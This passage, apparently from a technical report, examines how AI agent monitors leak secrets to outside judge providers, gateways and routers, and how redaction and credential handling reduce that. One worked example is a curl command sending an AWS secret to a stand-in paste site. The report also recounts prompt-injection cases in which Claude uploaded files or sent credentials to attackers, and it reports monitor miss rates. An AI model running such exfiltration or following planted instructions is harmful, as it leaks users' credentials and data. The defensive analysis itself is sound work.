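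To demonstrate the 99.95% recall needed to protect a hundred secrets, as calculated earlier, a detector would have to catch about 6,000 secrets without a miss. SecretBench has only 4,457 different secrets. A company could reach 6,000 by planting fake secrets in its transcripts, but this would test only the formats that someone thought to include.

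## What the provider and an intermediary can see and keep

If a redactor misses "marigold", the judge's provider receives the word with the rest of the payload, including the three customer records. The damage depends on how long the provider keeps the request, who there can read it, and which other companies handled it on the way.

### What OpenAI keeps

With Watcher's default settings, OpenAI receives every tool call that the local rules can't settle. OpenAI says that since March 2023 it has not used API data to train its models unless the customer opts in, so a password in a payload should not turn up in a later model's output. But OpenAI still stores copies of the text for other reasons.

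OpenAI keeps abuse monitoring logs to look for customers who break its rules. These logs can contain prompts and replies, as well as the output of classifiers that OpenAI runs on them. By default, OpenAI keeps the logs for up to 30 days.

Some API features also save data for the customer's program to use later. OpenAI calls this data application state, and the amount saved depends on the endpoint, which is the API address the program calls.

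| Endpoint | What OpenAI saves as application state by default |
| --- | --- |
| Chat Completions | Nothing, with exceptions such as audio |
| Responses | Response data, for at least 30 days |
| Conversations | The conversation, until the customer deletes it |

Two monitors that use the same OpenAI model can therefore leave different copies behind. A monitor that calls the Responses endpoint can avoid the extra copy by turning storage off in each request. To find out whether a monitor does this, a customer would have to ask its maker or look at the requests.

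OpenAI may also cache prompts, which means saving the results of processing a prompt so that a later request with the same beginning runs faster. Judge requests often share a beginning because each can repeat the same instructions and much of the same transcript. OpenAI says it may keep the cached data for up to 24 hours, encrypted, on the machine that processed it.

The 30-day period runs separately for each request. Suppose the agent in the invented session read `deploy.log` on March 1, and the developer resumed the session on March 20. If the payload for the next judged command still included the log, OpenAI could hold that copy of the customer records until April 19. A long session can produce hundreds of requests, and any of them might contain the log.

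OpenAI can keep logs for longer than 30 days if the law requires it or if it is "reasonably necessary" to protect its services or anyone else from harm. For example, if a court ordered OpenAI to preserve its logs as evidence in a lawsuit, Cy Example's overdue payment could stay in them until the order ended, even if neither Cy nor the developer had any connection to the case.

The exception for harm may apply to monitors' requests more often than to other customers' requests. A monitor sends the judge commands that might be dangerous, so its requests can look like an attack. Watcher's backup models for refused requests suggest that Apollo expects this. OpenAI could therefore be most likely to flag and keep the sessions that a monitor rates as most dangerous.

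OpenAI's documentation describes one special arrangement that excludes stored content from human review. This implies that people at OpenAI may read content in the ordinary logs, so customers should assume they can.

### Zero data retention

Some customers can get OpenAI to keep less data if OpenAI approves them and they accept additional requirements. They remain responsible for ensuring their users follow OpenAI's policies. An approved customer can apply either of two settings to its whole organisation or to a single project.

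Under Modified Abuse Monitoring, OpenAI leaves prompts and replies out of its abuse logs, except in rare cases involving images and files. Zero Data Retention does the same and also turns off storage on the Responses and Chat Completions endpoints, even if a program requests storage. This protects customers whose monitor leaves storage on by mistake.

The word "zero" is somewhat misleading, because the temporary prompt cache can still exist and endpoints that don't support the setting, such as Conversations, may still save content. If the judge can call an outside service, that service's retention rules apply to whatever it receives. OpenAI also keeps any image that its classifier flags as possible child sexual abuse material so that a person can review it, but a judge that receives only text would not trigger this rule.

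OpenAI can also withdraw Zero Data Retention from a particular customer for particular models, after notifying the customer in writing. It does this in one of two ways:

| Arrangement | What OpenAI may keep | Who may read it |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Safety Retention | Content that its classifiers flag as a possible violation | OpenAI's reviewers |
| Private Retention with Private Safety Processing | Customer content, in encrypted logs | No human reviewer, unless the law requires it |

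OpenAI reserves Safety Retention for cases where it is reasonably necessary to investigate or prevent "severe risk activity". A company that relies on Zero Data Retention for its judge should make sure any notice of Safety Retention reaches someone who knows what the monitor sends.

Despite these exceptions, the setting removes most of what a thief or a court could obtain later. An order to preserve existing logs has little effect on content that OpenAI never logged, although a court could perhaps order it to start keeping more.

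Zero Data Retention is set on the OpenAI account that makes the request, so a company that hosts Watcher itself can apply for it on its own account. With Watcher Cloud, Apollo makes the requests, so the customer depends on Apollo's terms with OpenAI. In both cases, the transcript also remains in Watcher's database, which OpenAI's settings don't affect.

Customers can also choose where OpenAI stores their content, but in some regions this doesn't determine where the model runs. A customer that selects the United Kingdom, for example, gets storage there, but OpenAI may process the text and temporarily store it in another country.

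Even a direct connection to OpenAI can involve another company. For its regional US and EU addresses, OpenAI uses a service from Cloudflare, a network company, to keep decryption in the chosen region. This suggests that Cloudflare's equipment holds the request in plaintext before OpenAI's does.

Watcher's default judges come from two providers, each with its own terms. Zero Data Retention at OpenAI does not cover the copy that Anthropic receives when the fast judge passes a call on.

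### What a gateway adds

A gateway, or router, holds each judge request in plaintext while forwarding it, so the customer has to trust more than the gateway company's good intentions.

Staff at the company running the gateway may have access to its servers, and its logs and backups may contain the text long after the request has finished. The gateway also runs third-party software, and a malicious update to any of it could read whatever the gateway handles.

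The gateway usually also decides which provider receives the request. Several companies can offer the same model under the same name, as Anthropic, Amazon, Google and Microsoft do with Claude, and each has its own terms. If one provider fails to answer and the gateway tries another, both may have received the payload.

According to Help Net Security's *Command integrity breaks in the LLM routing layer*, a request can pass through several gateways, each of which can read it, while the customer configures and sees only the first. A contract with the company running the first gateway gives the customer little control over the others unless it restricts where that company may send data.

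A customer can't tell from the replies what the provider or an intermediary has seen or kept. Wu, Zhao and colleagues (2026) point out in *What the Middleman Delivers* that a router can return correct answers and still store every conversation.

### A company's own gateway and a commercial aggregator

Some companies run their own gateway, often with open-source software such as LiteLLM. Others use a commercial aggregator such as OpenRouter, which offers models from many providers through one account. An important difference is that an aggregator normally replaces the customer's key with its own, so the provider bills the aggregator's account for the request.

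A company that has Zero Data Retention on its own OpenAI account can lose that protection if its judge calls go out under an aggregator's key, because the aggregator's settings then apply.

*CacheProbe* (2026) found that shared keys could also reveal information about one customer's prompts to another. Providers keep different organisations' prompt caches separate to prevent this, but OpenRouter's customers shared its provider accounts, so to the provider they all looked like one organisation. Anyone with an ordinary OpenRouter account and some credit could test whether a prompt was already in the cache, and potentially reconstruct text that another customer had sent.

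For a judge, the most likely leak is probably that an outsider could confirm a guess about its instructions, which are the same in every request. Recovering a particular log file would be harder, because the outsider would also have to match everything before it in the prompt.

OpenRouter lets customers supply their own provider keys, which restored the separation. *CacheProbe* found no statistically significant sign of sharing between accounts that used their own keys at any provider. OpenRouter still handles the requests in plaintext, so using their own keys protects customers from each other but not from OpenRouter.

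| | Gateway run by the user's organisation | Commercial aggregator |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Who can read requests at the gateway | The organisation's own administrators | The aggregator's staff |
| Whose provider account | The organisation's | The aggregator's, unless the customer supplies keys |
| Provider's retention setting | The organisation can apply for it | The aggregator's, unless the customer supplies keys |
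| Who picks the provider | The organisation | The aggregator, within any limits the customer can set |
| Who must fix security flaws | The organisation | The aggregator |

A company that runs its own gateway avoids giving the text to another company, but it has to maintain the gateway. In *Your Agent Has a Middleman You Didn't Vet*, the blogger Crosley (2026) counts eleven security flaws in the LiteLLM gateway that a Python vulnerability database added on October 1, 2026. One let anyone with an account on the gateway obtain the provider keys stored there. LiteLLM had released fixes in August, so only companies that hadn't updated were still exposed in October.

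### Routers that misused what they received

In *Your Agent Is Mine*, Liu, Shou and colleagues (2026) measured how often routers abuse their position. They bought access to 28 routers from sellers on Taobao, Xianyu and Shopify-hosted shops, and collected 400 free ones from public communities.

According to Crosley, who worked from the full paper, the researchers opened an account on each router and ran a coding agent through it on randomly selected programming tasks. The agent ran in a sandbox, an isolated environment where a harmful command could do no real damage. The sandbox ran every command that came back and recorded network connections, changed files and new processes. A second agent then reviewed anything suspicious.

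To find out whether routers stole secrets, the researchers sent some of their own secrets through them. These included *canary credentials*, working AWS keys that nobody else had a reason to use. If someone else later used one, it must have leaked on the way.

| What happened | Paid routers (28) | Free routers (400) |
| --- | --- | --- |
| The router changed a reply to include an attacker's command or software package | 1 | 8 |
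| Someone used a planted AWS key after it passed through | 0 | 17 |
| Someone emptied a planted cryptocurrency wallet | 0 | 1 |

The wallet held less than $50. An altered reply could also change a judge's verdict, for instance from "block" to "allow".

The AWS result is a minimum, because the table would not include a router that copied a key without using it or one that stored private files. A planted key also doesn't identify the thief, who could have been anyone further along the chain.

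None of the 28 paid routers stole keys, which is weak evidence that paying for a router makes it safer. Among free routers, 17 of 400 (4.25%) did. If paid routers stole keys at the same rate, a sample of 28 would contain no thefts about 30% of the time, since 0.9575²⁸ ≈ 0.30.

Short tests can also miss a router that alters replies. Two of the free routers changed replies only under certain conditions, and one behaved normally for the first 50 requests. Other routers may have changed replies under conditions that the researchers' tests never met.

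These rates don't apply to the whole industry. According to Crosley, most of the sample came from Chinese-language marketplaces and communities, and most of the free routers used one of two open-source templates. The study left out enterprise gateways and did not test OpenRouter or LiteLLM. It shows that some cheap and free routers steal credentials, but it gives no rate for gateways that a company runs itself or buys under contract.

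*Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?* (2026) raises a different limitation, that the counts don't show how an agent responds to an altered reply. The agent might ask its user for permission and never run the command. This limitation matters less for secrets, because the router has already received them by the time the agent acts.

Liu and colleagues also set up poorly secured routers as decoys. Other people began sending traffic through them, and the decoys became part of chains that served real users. They handled about 2 billion tokens and exposed 99 different credentials across 440 Codex sessions. The users of those sessions could not tell that their text was passing through the decoys.

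That is about one credential for every four or five sessions, which gives a rough idea of how often real agent traffic contains secrets. The share of sessions with a secret may be lower, because one session can contain many. People who use such routers may also handle credentials less carefully than a company's engineers. On the other hand, the researchers could count only what they recognised as a credential, so they may have missed passwords like "marigold". In 401 of the 440 sessions, the agent could run commands without asking, the kind of use that leads people to add a monitor.

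Wu and colleagues later tested 20 more conventional routers that sold access to GPT-6 Astra or Claude Opus 5. They required most of these to have an English website, public prices, and payment by card or PayPal. They screened 3,332 replies to requests for code and setup instructions and did not confirm any injected code. But their requests were short, contained no credentials and did not come from a working agent, so they might not have triggered the behaviour that Liu and colleagues found. Wu and colleagues warn against combining the two studies' rates.

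Seven of the ten cheap routers, and two of the ten that charged official prices or more, also gave answers that differed measurably from the official API's for at least one model, which is a problem for judges that use them. With so few routers, the gap between the groups could be due to chance (p = 0.07). A router might have substituted a cheaper model, changed the settings or added instructions, and the test can't distinguish between these causes.

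If the router switched models, the customer is no longer using the judge whose accuracy it checked. The transcript may also have gone to a provider that the customer never approved.

Five routers reported between 4,200 and 60,000 more input tokens than the official API did for identical requests. They may have added hidden text to the prompt or only inflated the count. One router where the researchers could check the account balance charged for the extra tokens.

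### The LiteLLM compromise

A company that runs its own gateway still depends on the people who write the software. On March 24, 2026, attackers uploaded two versions of the LiteLLM gateway package to PyPI, the public index from which most Python programs get their components. Both versions contained code for stealing credentials.

According to LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026), the code searched for cloud keys, SSH keys, database passwords and environment variables, which often hold secrets, and sent what it found to a web address that resembled one of LiteLLM's own. A gateway is an attractive target because it can hold an organisation's keys for every model provider.

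In *Security Townhall Updates*, LiteLLM's chief executive and chief technology officer, Dholakia and Jaff (2026), trace the attack to a security scanner called Trivy. LiteLLM's build system ran Trivy without specifying a version, so it picked up a compromised copy. All the build steps shared one environment, which also contained long-lived passwords for publishing releases. The attackers apparently took those passwords and uploaded their own packages directly to PyPI.

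LiteLLM found no malicious code in the main branch of its public source, so a customer who had reviewed that source before installing the package would have found nothing wrong.

Accounts of the attack disagree about its cause. Help Net Security attributes it to dependency confusion, in which an installer fetches an attacker's package instead of an internal one with the same name. Crosley says that the paper by Liu and colleagues does too. PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026) and LiteLLM attribute it to credentials exposed through Trivy. Their account is more credible because PyPI and LiteLLM investigated the incident and had access to the accounts involved.

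The sources also disagree about how long the packages were available. LiteLLM says about 40 minutes. PyPI says 2 hours and 32 minutes from upload to quarantine, and divides this into the time before the first report and the response time. PyPI's figure is probably better because PyPI carried out the quarantine. LiteLLM itself advises anyone who installed the package between 10:39 and 16:00 UTC that day to check for the bad versions.

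PyPI counted more than 119,000 downloads of the two versions, but automated systems often download the same package many times, so this is not a count of victims. LiteLLM says its cloud service and official container image were unaffected. The image used pinned versions of its components and did not install the bad packages.

It is less clear whether the attackers obtained any prompts. Both versions had malicious code in the gateway's server program, and Help Net Security says this code had access to every request and response. LiteLLM describes only stolen credentials, while PyPI says the code also took sensitive files. The attackers may have had access to a customer's transcripts, but none of these accounts reports that they copied any.

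Redacting the payload would not have protected the gateway's own keys, which were on the same machine, but waiting before installing new releases would have. PyPI recommends configuring the installer to ignore packages published in the last few days, and a three-day wait would easily have outlasted this attack. But waiting also delays urgent security fixes, unless the company makes an exception for them.

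### Hiding the text from the gateway's operator

Liu and colleagues want providers to sign their replies so that a customer could detect any change a router made. The router could still read any secrets in the request, because it receives the request before the provider does.

Xie and colleagues designed a router called AEGIS to address both problems. It handles the text inside an *enclave*, a part of the computer that the hardware isolates from the rest, including the operating system and its administrators. The operator still manages accounts and billing on the ordinary part of the machine, which Xie and colleagues call the host.

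The customer needs a way to know which program the enclave is running. The hardware provides this through *attestation*, a signed statement that contains a fingerprint of the program. The fingerprint is a hash, so changing the program changes the fingerprint. AEGIS uses it in this order:

1. Before first use, the customer reviews the enclave's source code, builds the program from it and records the fingerprint. The customer's software also checks that the operator has published the same build in a public log.
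2. At the start of a session, a small program on the customer's machine, the *sidecar*, sends the enclave a random number and receives an attestation.
3. The sidecar checks the hardware maker's signature and confirms that nobody is running the enclave in debugging mode.
4. It compares the fingerprint with the recorded one. It also checks that the attestation includes its random number, which rules out an old statement, and the certificate of the current connection, which rules out a statement from a different machine.
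5. If every check passes, the sidecar sends the request. If any check fails, it sends nothing.
6. The enclave asks the host which provider account to use, then forwards the request unchanged. The host can choose only from a list of destinations built into the program.

Xie and colleagues say that earlier enclave gateways let the customer check the attestation only after sending the request. If the check fails, any secret in the request has already leaked, and the leak can't be undone.

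Attestation proves which program is running but not that the program is safe, so somebody has to read the code. Xie and colleagues kept the part of AEGIS that handles text to 851 lines. By a broader count, AEGIS has 1,236 lines, compared with 10,434 in the closest open-source alternative. They also tested coding agents on ten faults planted in the code. Claude Code found all ten and Codex found eight. This is encouraging, but the test was small and the researchers chose the faults, so it doesn't show that an agent would catch a fault carefully hidden by a dishonest operator.

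AEGIS adds a median delay of 5.7 milliseconds to a small request. The enclave and its checks account for about 2 milliseconds of that, and ordinary forwarding accounts for the rest. The delay grows with request size, reaching 52 milliseconds for one megabyte. Judge payloads can be long, but even 52 milliseconds is short next to a model call, which takes about a second.

In tests of an AEGIS prototype, the host could neither read nor change the text, although the same attacks worked on an ordinary router. The researchers built the prototype and chose the attacks themselves. The results also depend on the hardware being sound. Other researchers have broken enclaves by observing a processor's behaviour from outside, and AEGIS does not defend against this.

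Even without reading the text, the operator can see the customer's account, the provider, the time of each request, the approximate lengths of the request and reply, and the number of tokens used. Suppose two payloads are identical except that one contains the password "marigold" and the other a different eight-letter password. If the replies also match in length and timing, the operator can't tell which payload the customer sent.

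The length of a judge's reply might be enough to guess the verdict, because judges often write more when they block a command than when they allow it. When a model streams its reply in small pieces, an observer may also be able to reconstruct some of the text from the sizes of the pieces. Padding the pieces to a standard size would help, but AEGIS doesn't do this yet.

A monitor would have to run the sidecar on whichever machine calls the judge. For a self-hosted Watcher, that is the customer's server. With Watcher Cloud it would be Apollo's, so AEGIS could hide the text from a router between Apollo and OpenAI but not from Apollo. Any redaction would have to happen before the text reaches the sidecar, because the enclave forwards it unchanged.

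AEGIS also assumes that the provider is honest. The enclave decrypts the request and sends it to the provider over an ordinary TLS connection. If the invented session went through AEGIS without redaction, the router's operator would see none of the six items, but OpenAI would receive all of them and could keep them in its logs for 30 days.

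## Ways to send fewer secrets, and what they cost the judge

To keep a secret from the judge's provider, the monitor has to send less, which may make the judge's decisions worse. How much worse depends on what the monitor leaves out.

### Judging with less text

Anthropic compared three inputs for auto mode's classifier and chose user messages and tool calls. Adding the agent's messages and the tool results made the classifier worse on a test of *overeager* actions, in which an agent tries to help but goes beyond what the user authorised. With tool calls alone, the classifier missed the fewest dangerous actions but blocked things that users had plainly asked for.

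Anthropic suspects that a longer transcript is harder to read and gives the agent's account of events more influence. It published no figures for the two rejected inputs. It also added the agent's messages and the tool results at the same time, so the comparison can't separate their effects.

For the input it chose, Anthropic reports these error rates:

| Test set | Size | Error | Quick filter alone | Both stages |
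| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Employees' real tool calls | 10,000 | Harmless actions blocked | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Real overeager actions | 52 | Dangerous actions missed | 6.6% | 17% |
| Synthetic attempts to send data out | 1,000 | Dangerous actions missed | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage removes false alarms but causes more misses. The 17% is nine actions out of 52. With so few cases, the true rate could plausibly be between about 9% and 30%.

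More text might not have prevented most of those misses. In most of the ones Anthropic examined, the classifier correctly identified the action as dangerous but wrongly classed it as one the user had agreed to. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" has not agreed to a force-push, which overwrites a branch's history on the server.

Leaving out tool results removes information about where a value came from. If a user says "cancel my job" and the agent cancels job `abc123`, the classifier can't determine whether the agent found that name in a query or made it up. Anthropic accepts this limitation in return for protection against instructions planted in tool results.

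Anthropic included or excluded whole kinds of text, and the classifier received any secrets in the included text unchanged, so none of these rates measures redaction.

A few well-chosen facts about the repository may make up for some of the missing text, and a monitor could look them up locally and send them without any file contents. After Apollo Research tested auto mode with synthetic attacks, Anthropic gave the classifier the Git status and other repository facts described earlier, along with new rules about sharing data. The miss rate on Apollo's attacks fell from 12% to 7%. On attacks that Anthropic had never had access to, the updated classifier caught about half of those the earlier version had missed, and missed about 2% of those the earlier version had caught. The 7% can't be compared with the 17% miss rate on the 52 real cases, because the attacks differ from those cases.

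*Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026) reports a less favourable figure. According to Machine Heart's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?*, auto mode missed 81% of the dangerous actions in the paper's 128 deliberately ambiguous scenarios. Many of these actions were edits to project files, which the classifier doesn't check, so sending it more information would not have caught them.

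The most detailed comparison of inputs is by Caldwell, Harley and colleagues (2026), in *ScopeJudge*. Their agents did penetration testing, which means attacking a client's systems with permission, and the user's request said what was off limits. Five professional testers labelled 4,897 tool calls, of which 7.7% were violations. Eight judges then reviewed each call with five amounts of context. The recall of four of them was:

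| What the judge received with the call and a general policy | GLM-5.2 | Claude Opus 4.8 | Claude Sonnet 4.6 | GPT-5.4-mini |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Nothing more | 0% | 2% | Under 1% | 25% |
| The user's message | 79% | 94% | 81% | 87% |
| The message and earlier tool calls | 87% | 86% | 43% | 76% |
| The same, with summaries of tool results | 86% | 86% | 40% | 69% |
| The full transcript | 86% | 84% | 44% | 63% |

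The user's message made by far the largest difference, so it is the last thing a monitor should withhold, even though it may contain a secret the developer typed, such as "marigold". Tool results barely changed the recall of the two strongest judges. Adding tool results and the agent's prose together raised GLM-5.2's precision only from 50% to 53%.

These tasks favour short payloads because the user stated the limits in the request. If only a configuration file shows that a database holds live customer data, a judge that can't see the file's contents may approve a command it should block. Caldwell and colleagues ran each combination once, so differences of a point or two may be noise. Their summaries would not protect secrets, because each judge model needed the full tool results to write its own.

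A monitor can also drop important text by accident. *Does the Judge See What the Evaluation Requires?* (2026) describes evaluation software that kept the text of messages but lost the tool calls. A redactor that rebuilds a JSON payload could lose them too, so its tests should check that the tool call under review reaches the judge intact.

### Keeping credentials away from the agent

A secret that never enters the transcript can't reach the judge. Auth0's *Want AI Agents That Don't Spill Secrets?* shows how to keep a server's key out of the transcript when an agent uses a tool to send notifications. The model supplies only the recipient and the message, and the tool's handler, which is ordinary program code, fetches the key when it runs. A common mistake is to make the key one of the tool's arguments and put it in the system prompt so that the model can supply it.

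In the invented session, a tool called `query_orders` could replace the `psql` command:

```
Agent proposes:   query_orders("select * from failed_imports")
Judge receives:   query_orders("select * from failed_imports")
Handler runs:     the same query, adding the password from a secret store
```

The handler has to add the password after the judge has approved the call; otherwise the judge receives it. The judge loses almost no information this way, because the query and the database the tool opens are still visible to it.

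An agent that can't read the database password can still misuse the access it gives. `query_orders("drop table customers")` would work if the account behind the stored password can delete tables, so that account should have narrow permissions. The tool can also leak the password in its result, for instance if a failed connection returns an error message with the full database address, including the password.

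Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes another gap. In Cowork, the company's desktop agent, real credentials stay in the computer's keychain, and the virtual machine that runs the agent's code gets a limited token for the session. An outside researcher showed that an attack could work without any of the user's credentials. A malicious file in the user's folder contained hidden instructions and an attacker's API key. Claude followed the instructions and used the key to upload other files to the attacker's Anthropic account. The network rules allowed the upload because it went to Anthropic's own API.

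Credential insertion also protects only the credentials that someone has moved. As long as `settings.env` is on the disk, the agent can read it. In an exercise at Anthropic, a researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code a prompt that told it to read the user's AWS credentials file and send the contents to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. Keeping such files out of the agent's reach or blocking the outgoing request would have prevented this.

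Developers can put decoys where an agent expects to find keys. *Caught in the Act(ivation)* (Chauhan and Revankar, 2026) describes a prototype in which only the program that runs the tools has the real credentials, and the model's context contains realistic fakes. A monitor can safely send these fakes to an outside judge, and any attempt to use one is a warning sign.

### Redacting registered values

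Software that already has a list of secrets can search for their exact values without having to recognise their format. Poolside, which makes coding agents, does this. An agent can refer to a secret by name, and the software fills in the value when needed. If the value then appears in a tool's output, the software replaces it before the agent receives the output. It then checks the output against 28 built-in patterns, plus any the customer has added.

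Exact-value redaction can catch several secrets that patterns missed earlier. If someone registers `fake-pw-4821`, the redactor can remove it from both the database address and `PGPASSWORD=fake-pw-4821`, which the label rule missed because the password's entropy was too low. It can also find the secret half of the AWS pair under a name like `BACKUP`. The judge loses little information, because the redactor removes only the value and leaves the server's name. By contrast, a sample pattern in Poolside's documentation removes the whole database address.

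Matching against registered secrets misses any secret that nobody registered, such as Dana's temporary password, which may exist only in her note. Encoding can also hide a registered value, as it can in GitHub Actions. A truncated private key won't match the full one either, although a redactor could search for each line of the key separately.

Poolside checks what the user types only against patterns, so if a developer typed "marigold" into a prompt, it would be sent to the model even if it were registered as a secret. A monitor that sends user messages to a judge should also search them for the exact values of registered secrets.

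If an ordinary word such as "marigold" is registered as a secret, the redactor also removes it from unrelated text, such as a list of flower names. Poolside warns the user when a value triggers more than three replacements in one step, and recommends longer, unique secrets. Redacting a word from familiar text can also reveal it. If the agent prints an alphabetical dictionary and one entry is missing between "marie" and "marijuana", anyone with the same dictionary can work out the password.

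### Returning only approved fields

None of these methods protects the three customer records. A tool can protect them by returning only the fields its developer has approved. Hex describes this approach in *Redaction fails open*, using the example of HeadlessTracker, a tool that reads cryptocurrency balances. Hex identifies itself as an AI agent that maintains the project, so this is an account of one project's design and not tested evidence, but the logic is easy to check.

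The tool builds a new result from named fields such as `symbol` and `quantity`, and never passes on the exchange's original response. If the exchange adds a field containing a secret, the tool leaves it out by default. A redactor would pass the new field along unless one of its rules matched.

For the invented session, a tool could read the import log and return this:

```
{"failed_rows": 3, "row_ids": [1001, 1002, 1003], "stage": "import"}
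```

The agent can continue its work, and neither its provider nor the judge receives the customers' names, phone numbers or payment details. The row numbers may still identify customers to anyone with access to the database.

Free text is the weak point. If the developer approves a `note` field that contains Dana's password, the password is sent too. Error messages are hard to limit to fixed fields, so Hex scrubs them with patterns. A coding agent with a shell can also bypass the tool by printing the log with `head`.

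A monitor could apply the same idea to the judge's payload alone. The agent would receive the full log and could work normally, while the judge would receive only the file's path, its size and whether the command succeeded. Like auto mode's classifier, the judge would then have difficulty tracing where a value came from.

### Running a judge or detector locally

A language model could find secrets that patterns miss, but an outside provider running the model would receive those secrets. If the agent's own provider runs it, no new party receives them. Otherwise, the model needs to run on the user's own machines.

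A local detector can be fairly small. The fine-tuned Llama model in the earlier tests has eight billion parameters, which take up about 16 GB at two bytes each, or 4 GB when compressed to four bits each. Patterns would still have to select candidates for it to check.

Running the judge itself locally goes further, because the outside company receives nothing. *Shall We Approve?* (2026) does this with Qwen3Guard-Gen-8B, a safety model that receives the user's request and the proposed command. The software blocks any command the model rates unsafe or controversial.

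Running a judge on a company's own hardware reduces accuracy, although the gap may be smaller than one would expect. Four of the eight judges tested by Caldwell and colleagues have downloadable weights, including GLM-5.2, which had the highest F1 score, 0.66. The researchers called these models through OpenRouter, so they measured what the models can do but not how well they run on a company's hardware.

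Qwen3.6-35B is a more realistic choice for a workstation, since its 35 billion parameters would fit in about 18 GB at four bits each. Given only the user's message, it caught 80% of violations with 39% precision, while Claude Opus 4.8 caught 94% with the same precision. Compressing Qwen to four bits could make it worse. Larger models aren't always better, though, since one with 550 billion parameters had a lower best F1 score than Qwen (0.47 against 0.57).

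A company could also have a local model handle easy cases and send only the hard ones out. Agyemang, Kponyo and colleagues (2026), in *LLM-Redactor*, tested this on synthetic prompts, 300 of which were configuration files and code full of secrets. A three-billion-parameter model kept 75% of these on the machine. The share of labelled secrets that went out complete was:

| Method | Secrets sent out |
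| --- | --- |
| Redaction only | 16% |
| Local model for easy requests, no redaction | 24% |
| Both | 4% |

The redaction figure excludes fragments. It doubled to 32% when Agyemang and colleagues also counted those of at least four characters. They didn't test the quality of the local model's answers.

This arrangement would protect an agent's session much less than it protects single prompts. Each judge request can contain the earlier transcript, so a single hard case could send out everything the agent has read so far. If a local judge settled 75% of calls, a session with 20 calls would have about a 0.3% chance (0.75²⁰) of sending none out, assuming the calls were independent. The hard cases would still need redaction.

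### Replacement markers

When a redactor removes a secret, its choice of marker affects what the judge can work out. Imagine that the agent in the invented session proposes to send the secret half of the AWS key to a public text-sharing site. If the redactor replaces every secret with the same marker, the judge receives:

```
From settings.env:
AWS_SECRET_ACCESS_KEY=[REDACTED]
DATABASE_URL=postgres://shop:[REDACTED]@db.example.com:5432/orders

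Proposed command:
curl -d "v=[REDACTED]" https://paste.example.net/new
```

The value in the command could be the AWS key, the database password, an access token for the site itself, or a harmless string that the redactor removed by mistake. A typed marker with a number removes the ambiguity:

```
From settings.env:
AWS_SECRET_ACCESS_KEY=[AWS_SECRET_1]
DATABASE_URL=postgres://shop:[DB_PASSWORD_1]@db.example.com:5432/orders

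Proposed command:
curl -d "v=[AWS_SECRET_1]" https://paste.example.net/new
```

The markers now show that the command sends a key from the settings file to an unrelated address, which is enough for the judge to block it. They can also help the judge approve legitimate work, such as the original `psql` command, where `[DB_PASSWORD_1]` would go to the server it belongs to. Numbered markers also solve the earlier problem with redacted commit identifiers, because two different commits get different markers.

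This works only if the redactor finds the value both times. A label rule would find the AWS secret after `AWS_SECRET_ACCESS_KEY=` but not after `v=`, so the judge's provider would still receive it. The redactor should therefore list each value it finds, then search the whole payload again and redact every exact match.

If the monitor withheld tool results, the marker would appear only in the command. The monitor could add a note such as "AWS_SECRET_1 first appeared in settings.env". That would give the judge some of the information that auto mode's classifier lacks, without sending the file.

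Agyemang and colleagues use numbered markers like these and keep the table matching markers to values only in memory. Their software makes a new table for each request, but a monitor would do better to keep one table for the whole session. If it renumbered the secrets after cutting the middle out of a long transcript, `[DB_PASSWORD_1]` could refer to different passwords in different requests.

Some tools insert realistic fake values instead of markers. *Veil-Then-Reveal* (2026) does this for personal data so that the outside model still receives natural text. *CuratorKIT* (2026), a tool for preparing training data, gives the same name the same substitute throughout one sample, then chooses new substitutes for the next so that nobody can link samples. Fake values are riskier in a judge's payload. If the software replaced `paste.example.net` with a plausible company server name, the judge might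 approve the upload.

Even a good marker reveals to the provider what kinds of secrets the session contains. If two accounts have the same marker, the provider also learns that they share a password.

### Hashed markers

If several machines have to give the same secret the same marker, numbering requires them to share a table. A developer might instead use a *hash*, a short code calculated from the secret. The same secret always produces the same hash, and nobody can run the calculation backwards.

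The judge's provider, or a thief with its logs, can recover a weak password without reversing its hash, by hashing every word in a dictionary and looking for a match. This would find "marigold" in well under a second. An attacker without a dictionary could try every string of eight lower-case letters, since there are only 26⁸, or about 209 billion. At ten billion hashes a second, which is realistic for a fast graphics card and a common hash such as SHA-256, that takes about 21 seconds.

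Shortening the hash doesn't help much. Eight hexadecimal digits allow about 4.3 billion values, so in a dictionary of 100,000 words the correct word will almost certainly be the only match. A random 40-character AWS secret is safe from this attack because there are too many possibilities to try.

A *keyed hash* such as HMAC also protects weak passwords. It combines the value with a random key that stays on the user's machines:

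marker = first 8 digits of HMAC(key, value)

The same password still produces the same marker, but someone who guesses "marigold" can't check the guess without the key. If the key leaks, weak passwords can be guessed from their stored markers. Using a new key for each session limits that damage, but then markers don't match across sessions. Within one session, plain numbering is simpler and safer, because `[DB_PASSWORD_1]` isn't calculated from the password.

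### Tests on masked text

No experiment published in 2025 or 2026 appears to have measured how redacting secrets from agent transcripts changes a judge's decisions. The closest results are about the quality of written answers.

Agyemang and colleagues had a small model answer 50 secret-heavy prompts with and without redaction. When the same model compared each pair of answers, it rated the one from the unredacted prompt as better 80% of the time. This result may not carry over to a judge, which only has to allow or block an action.

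In other tests, masking identifiers has both lowered and improved model performance. *On the Impact of Anonymization on the Performance of Large Language Models* (2026) reports that replacing names and places with numbered markers lowered scores by 0.22 to 0.47 on a test in which models had to combine facts from several documents. On another task, several models improved. *RAGAL* (2026) reports that a technical-support assistant wrote better answers after its developers masked identifiers in its source material, because it stopped copying details from old cases into new ones.

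How much redaction harms the judge's decisions probably depends on whether the task requires the hidden value itself. A judge rarely needs to see a password to decide whether a command is safe, but it may well need a server name, a commit identifier or a public key. If so, most of the harm would come from redactors that remove too much.

A company could test how redaction affects the judge's decisions, without disclosing real secrets, by planting fake ones in recorded sessions. It would give the judge each session once with the fake secrets visible, once with bare markers in their place and once with numbered markers, then count the decisions that changed. The sessions should include both leaks and legitimate uses of a credential. Running the unredacted version twice would show how often the judge's decisions vary on identical input.

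The judge's instructions should also explain the markers, or the judge may treat missing text as suspicious. *trajectory-judge* (2026) includes a similar warning for judges that receive only an agent's final outcome: "Not being able to see the steps is not evidence of a failure".
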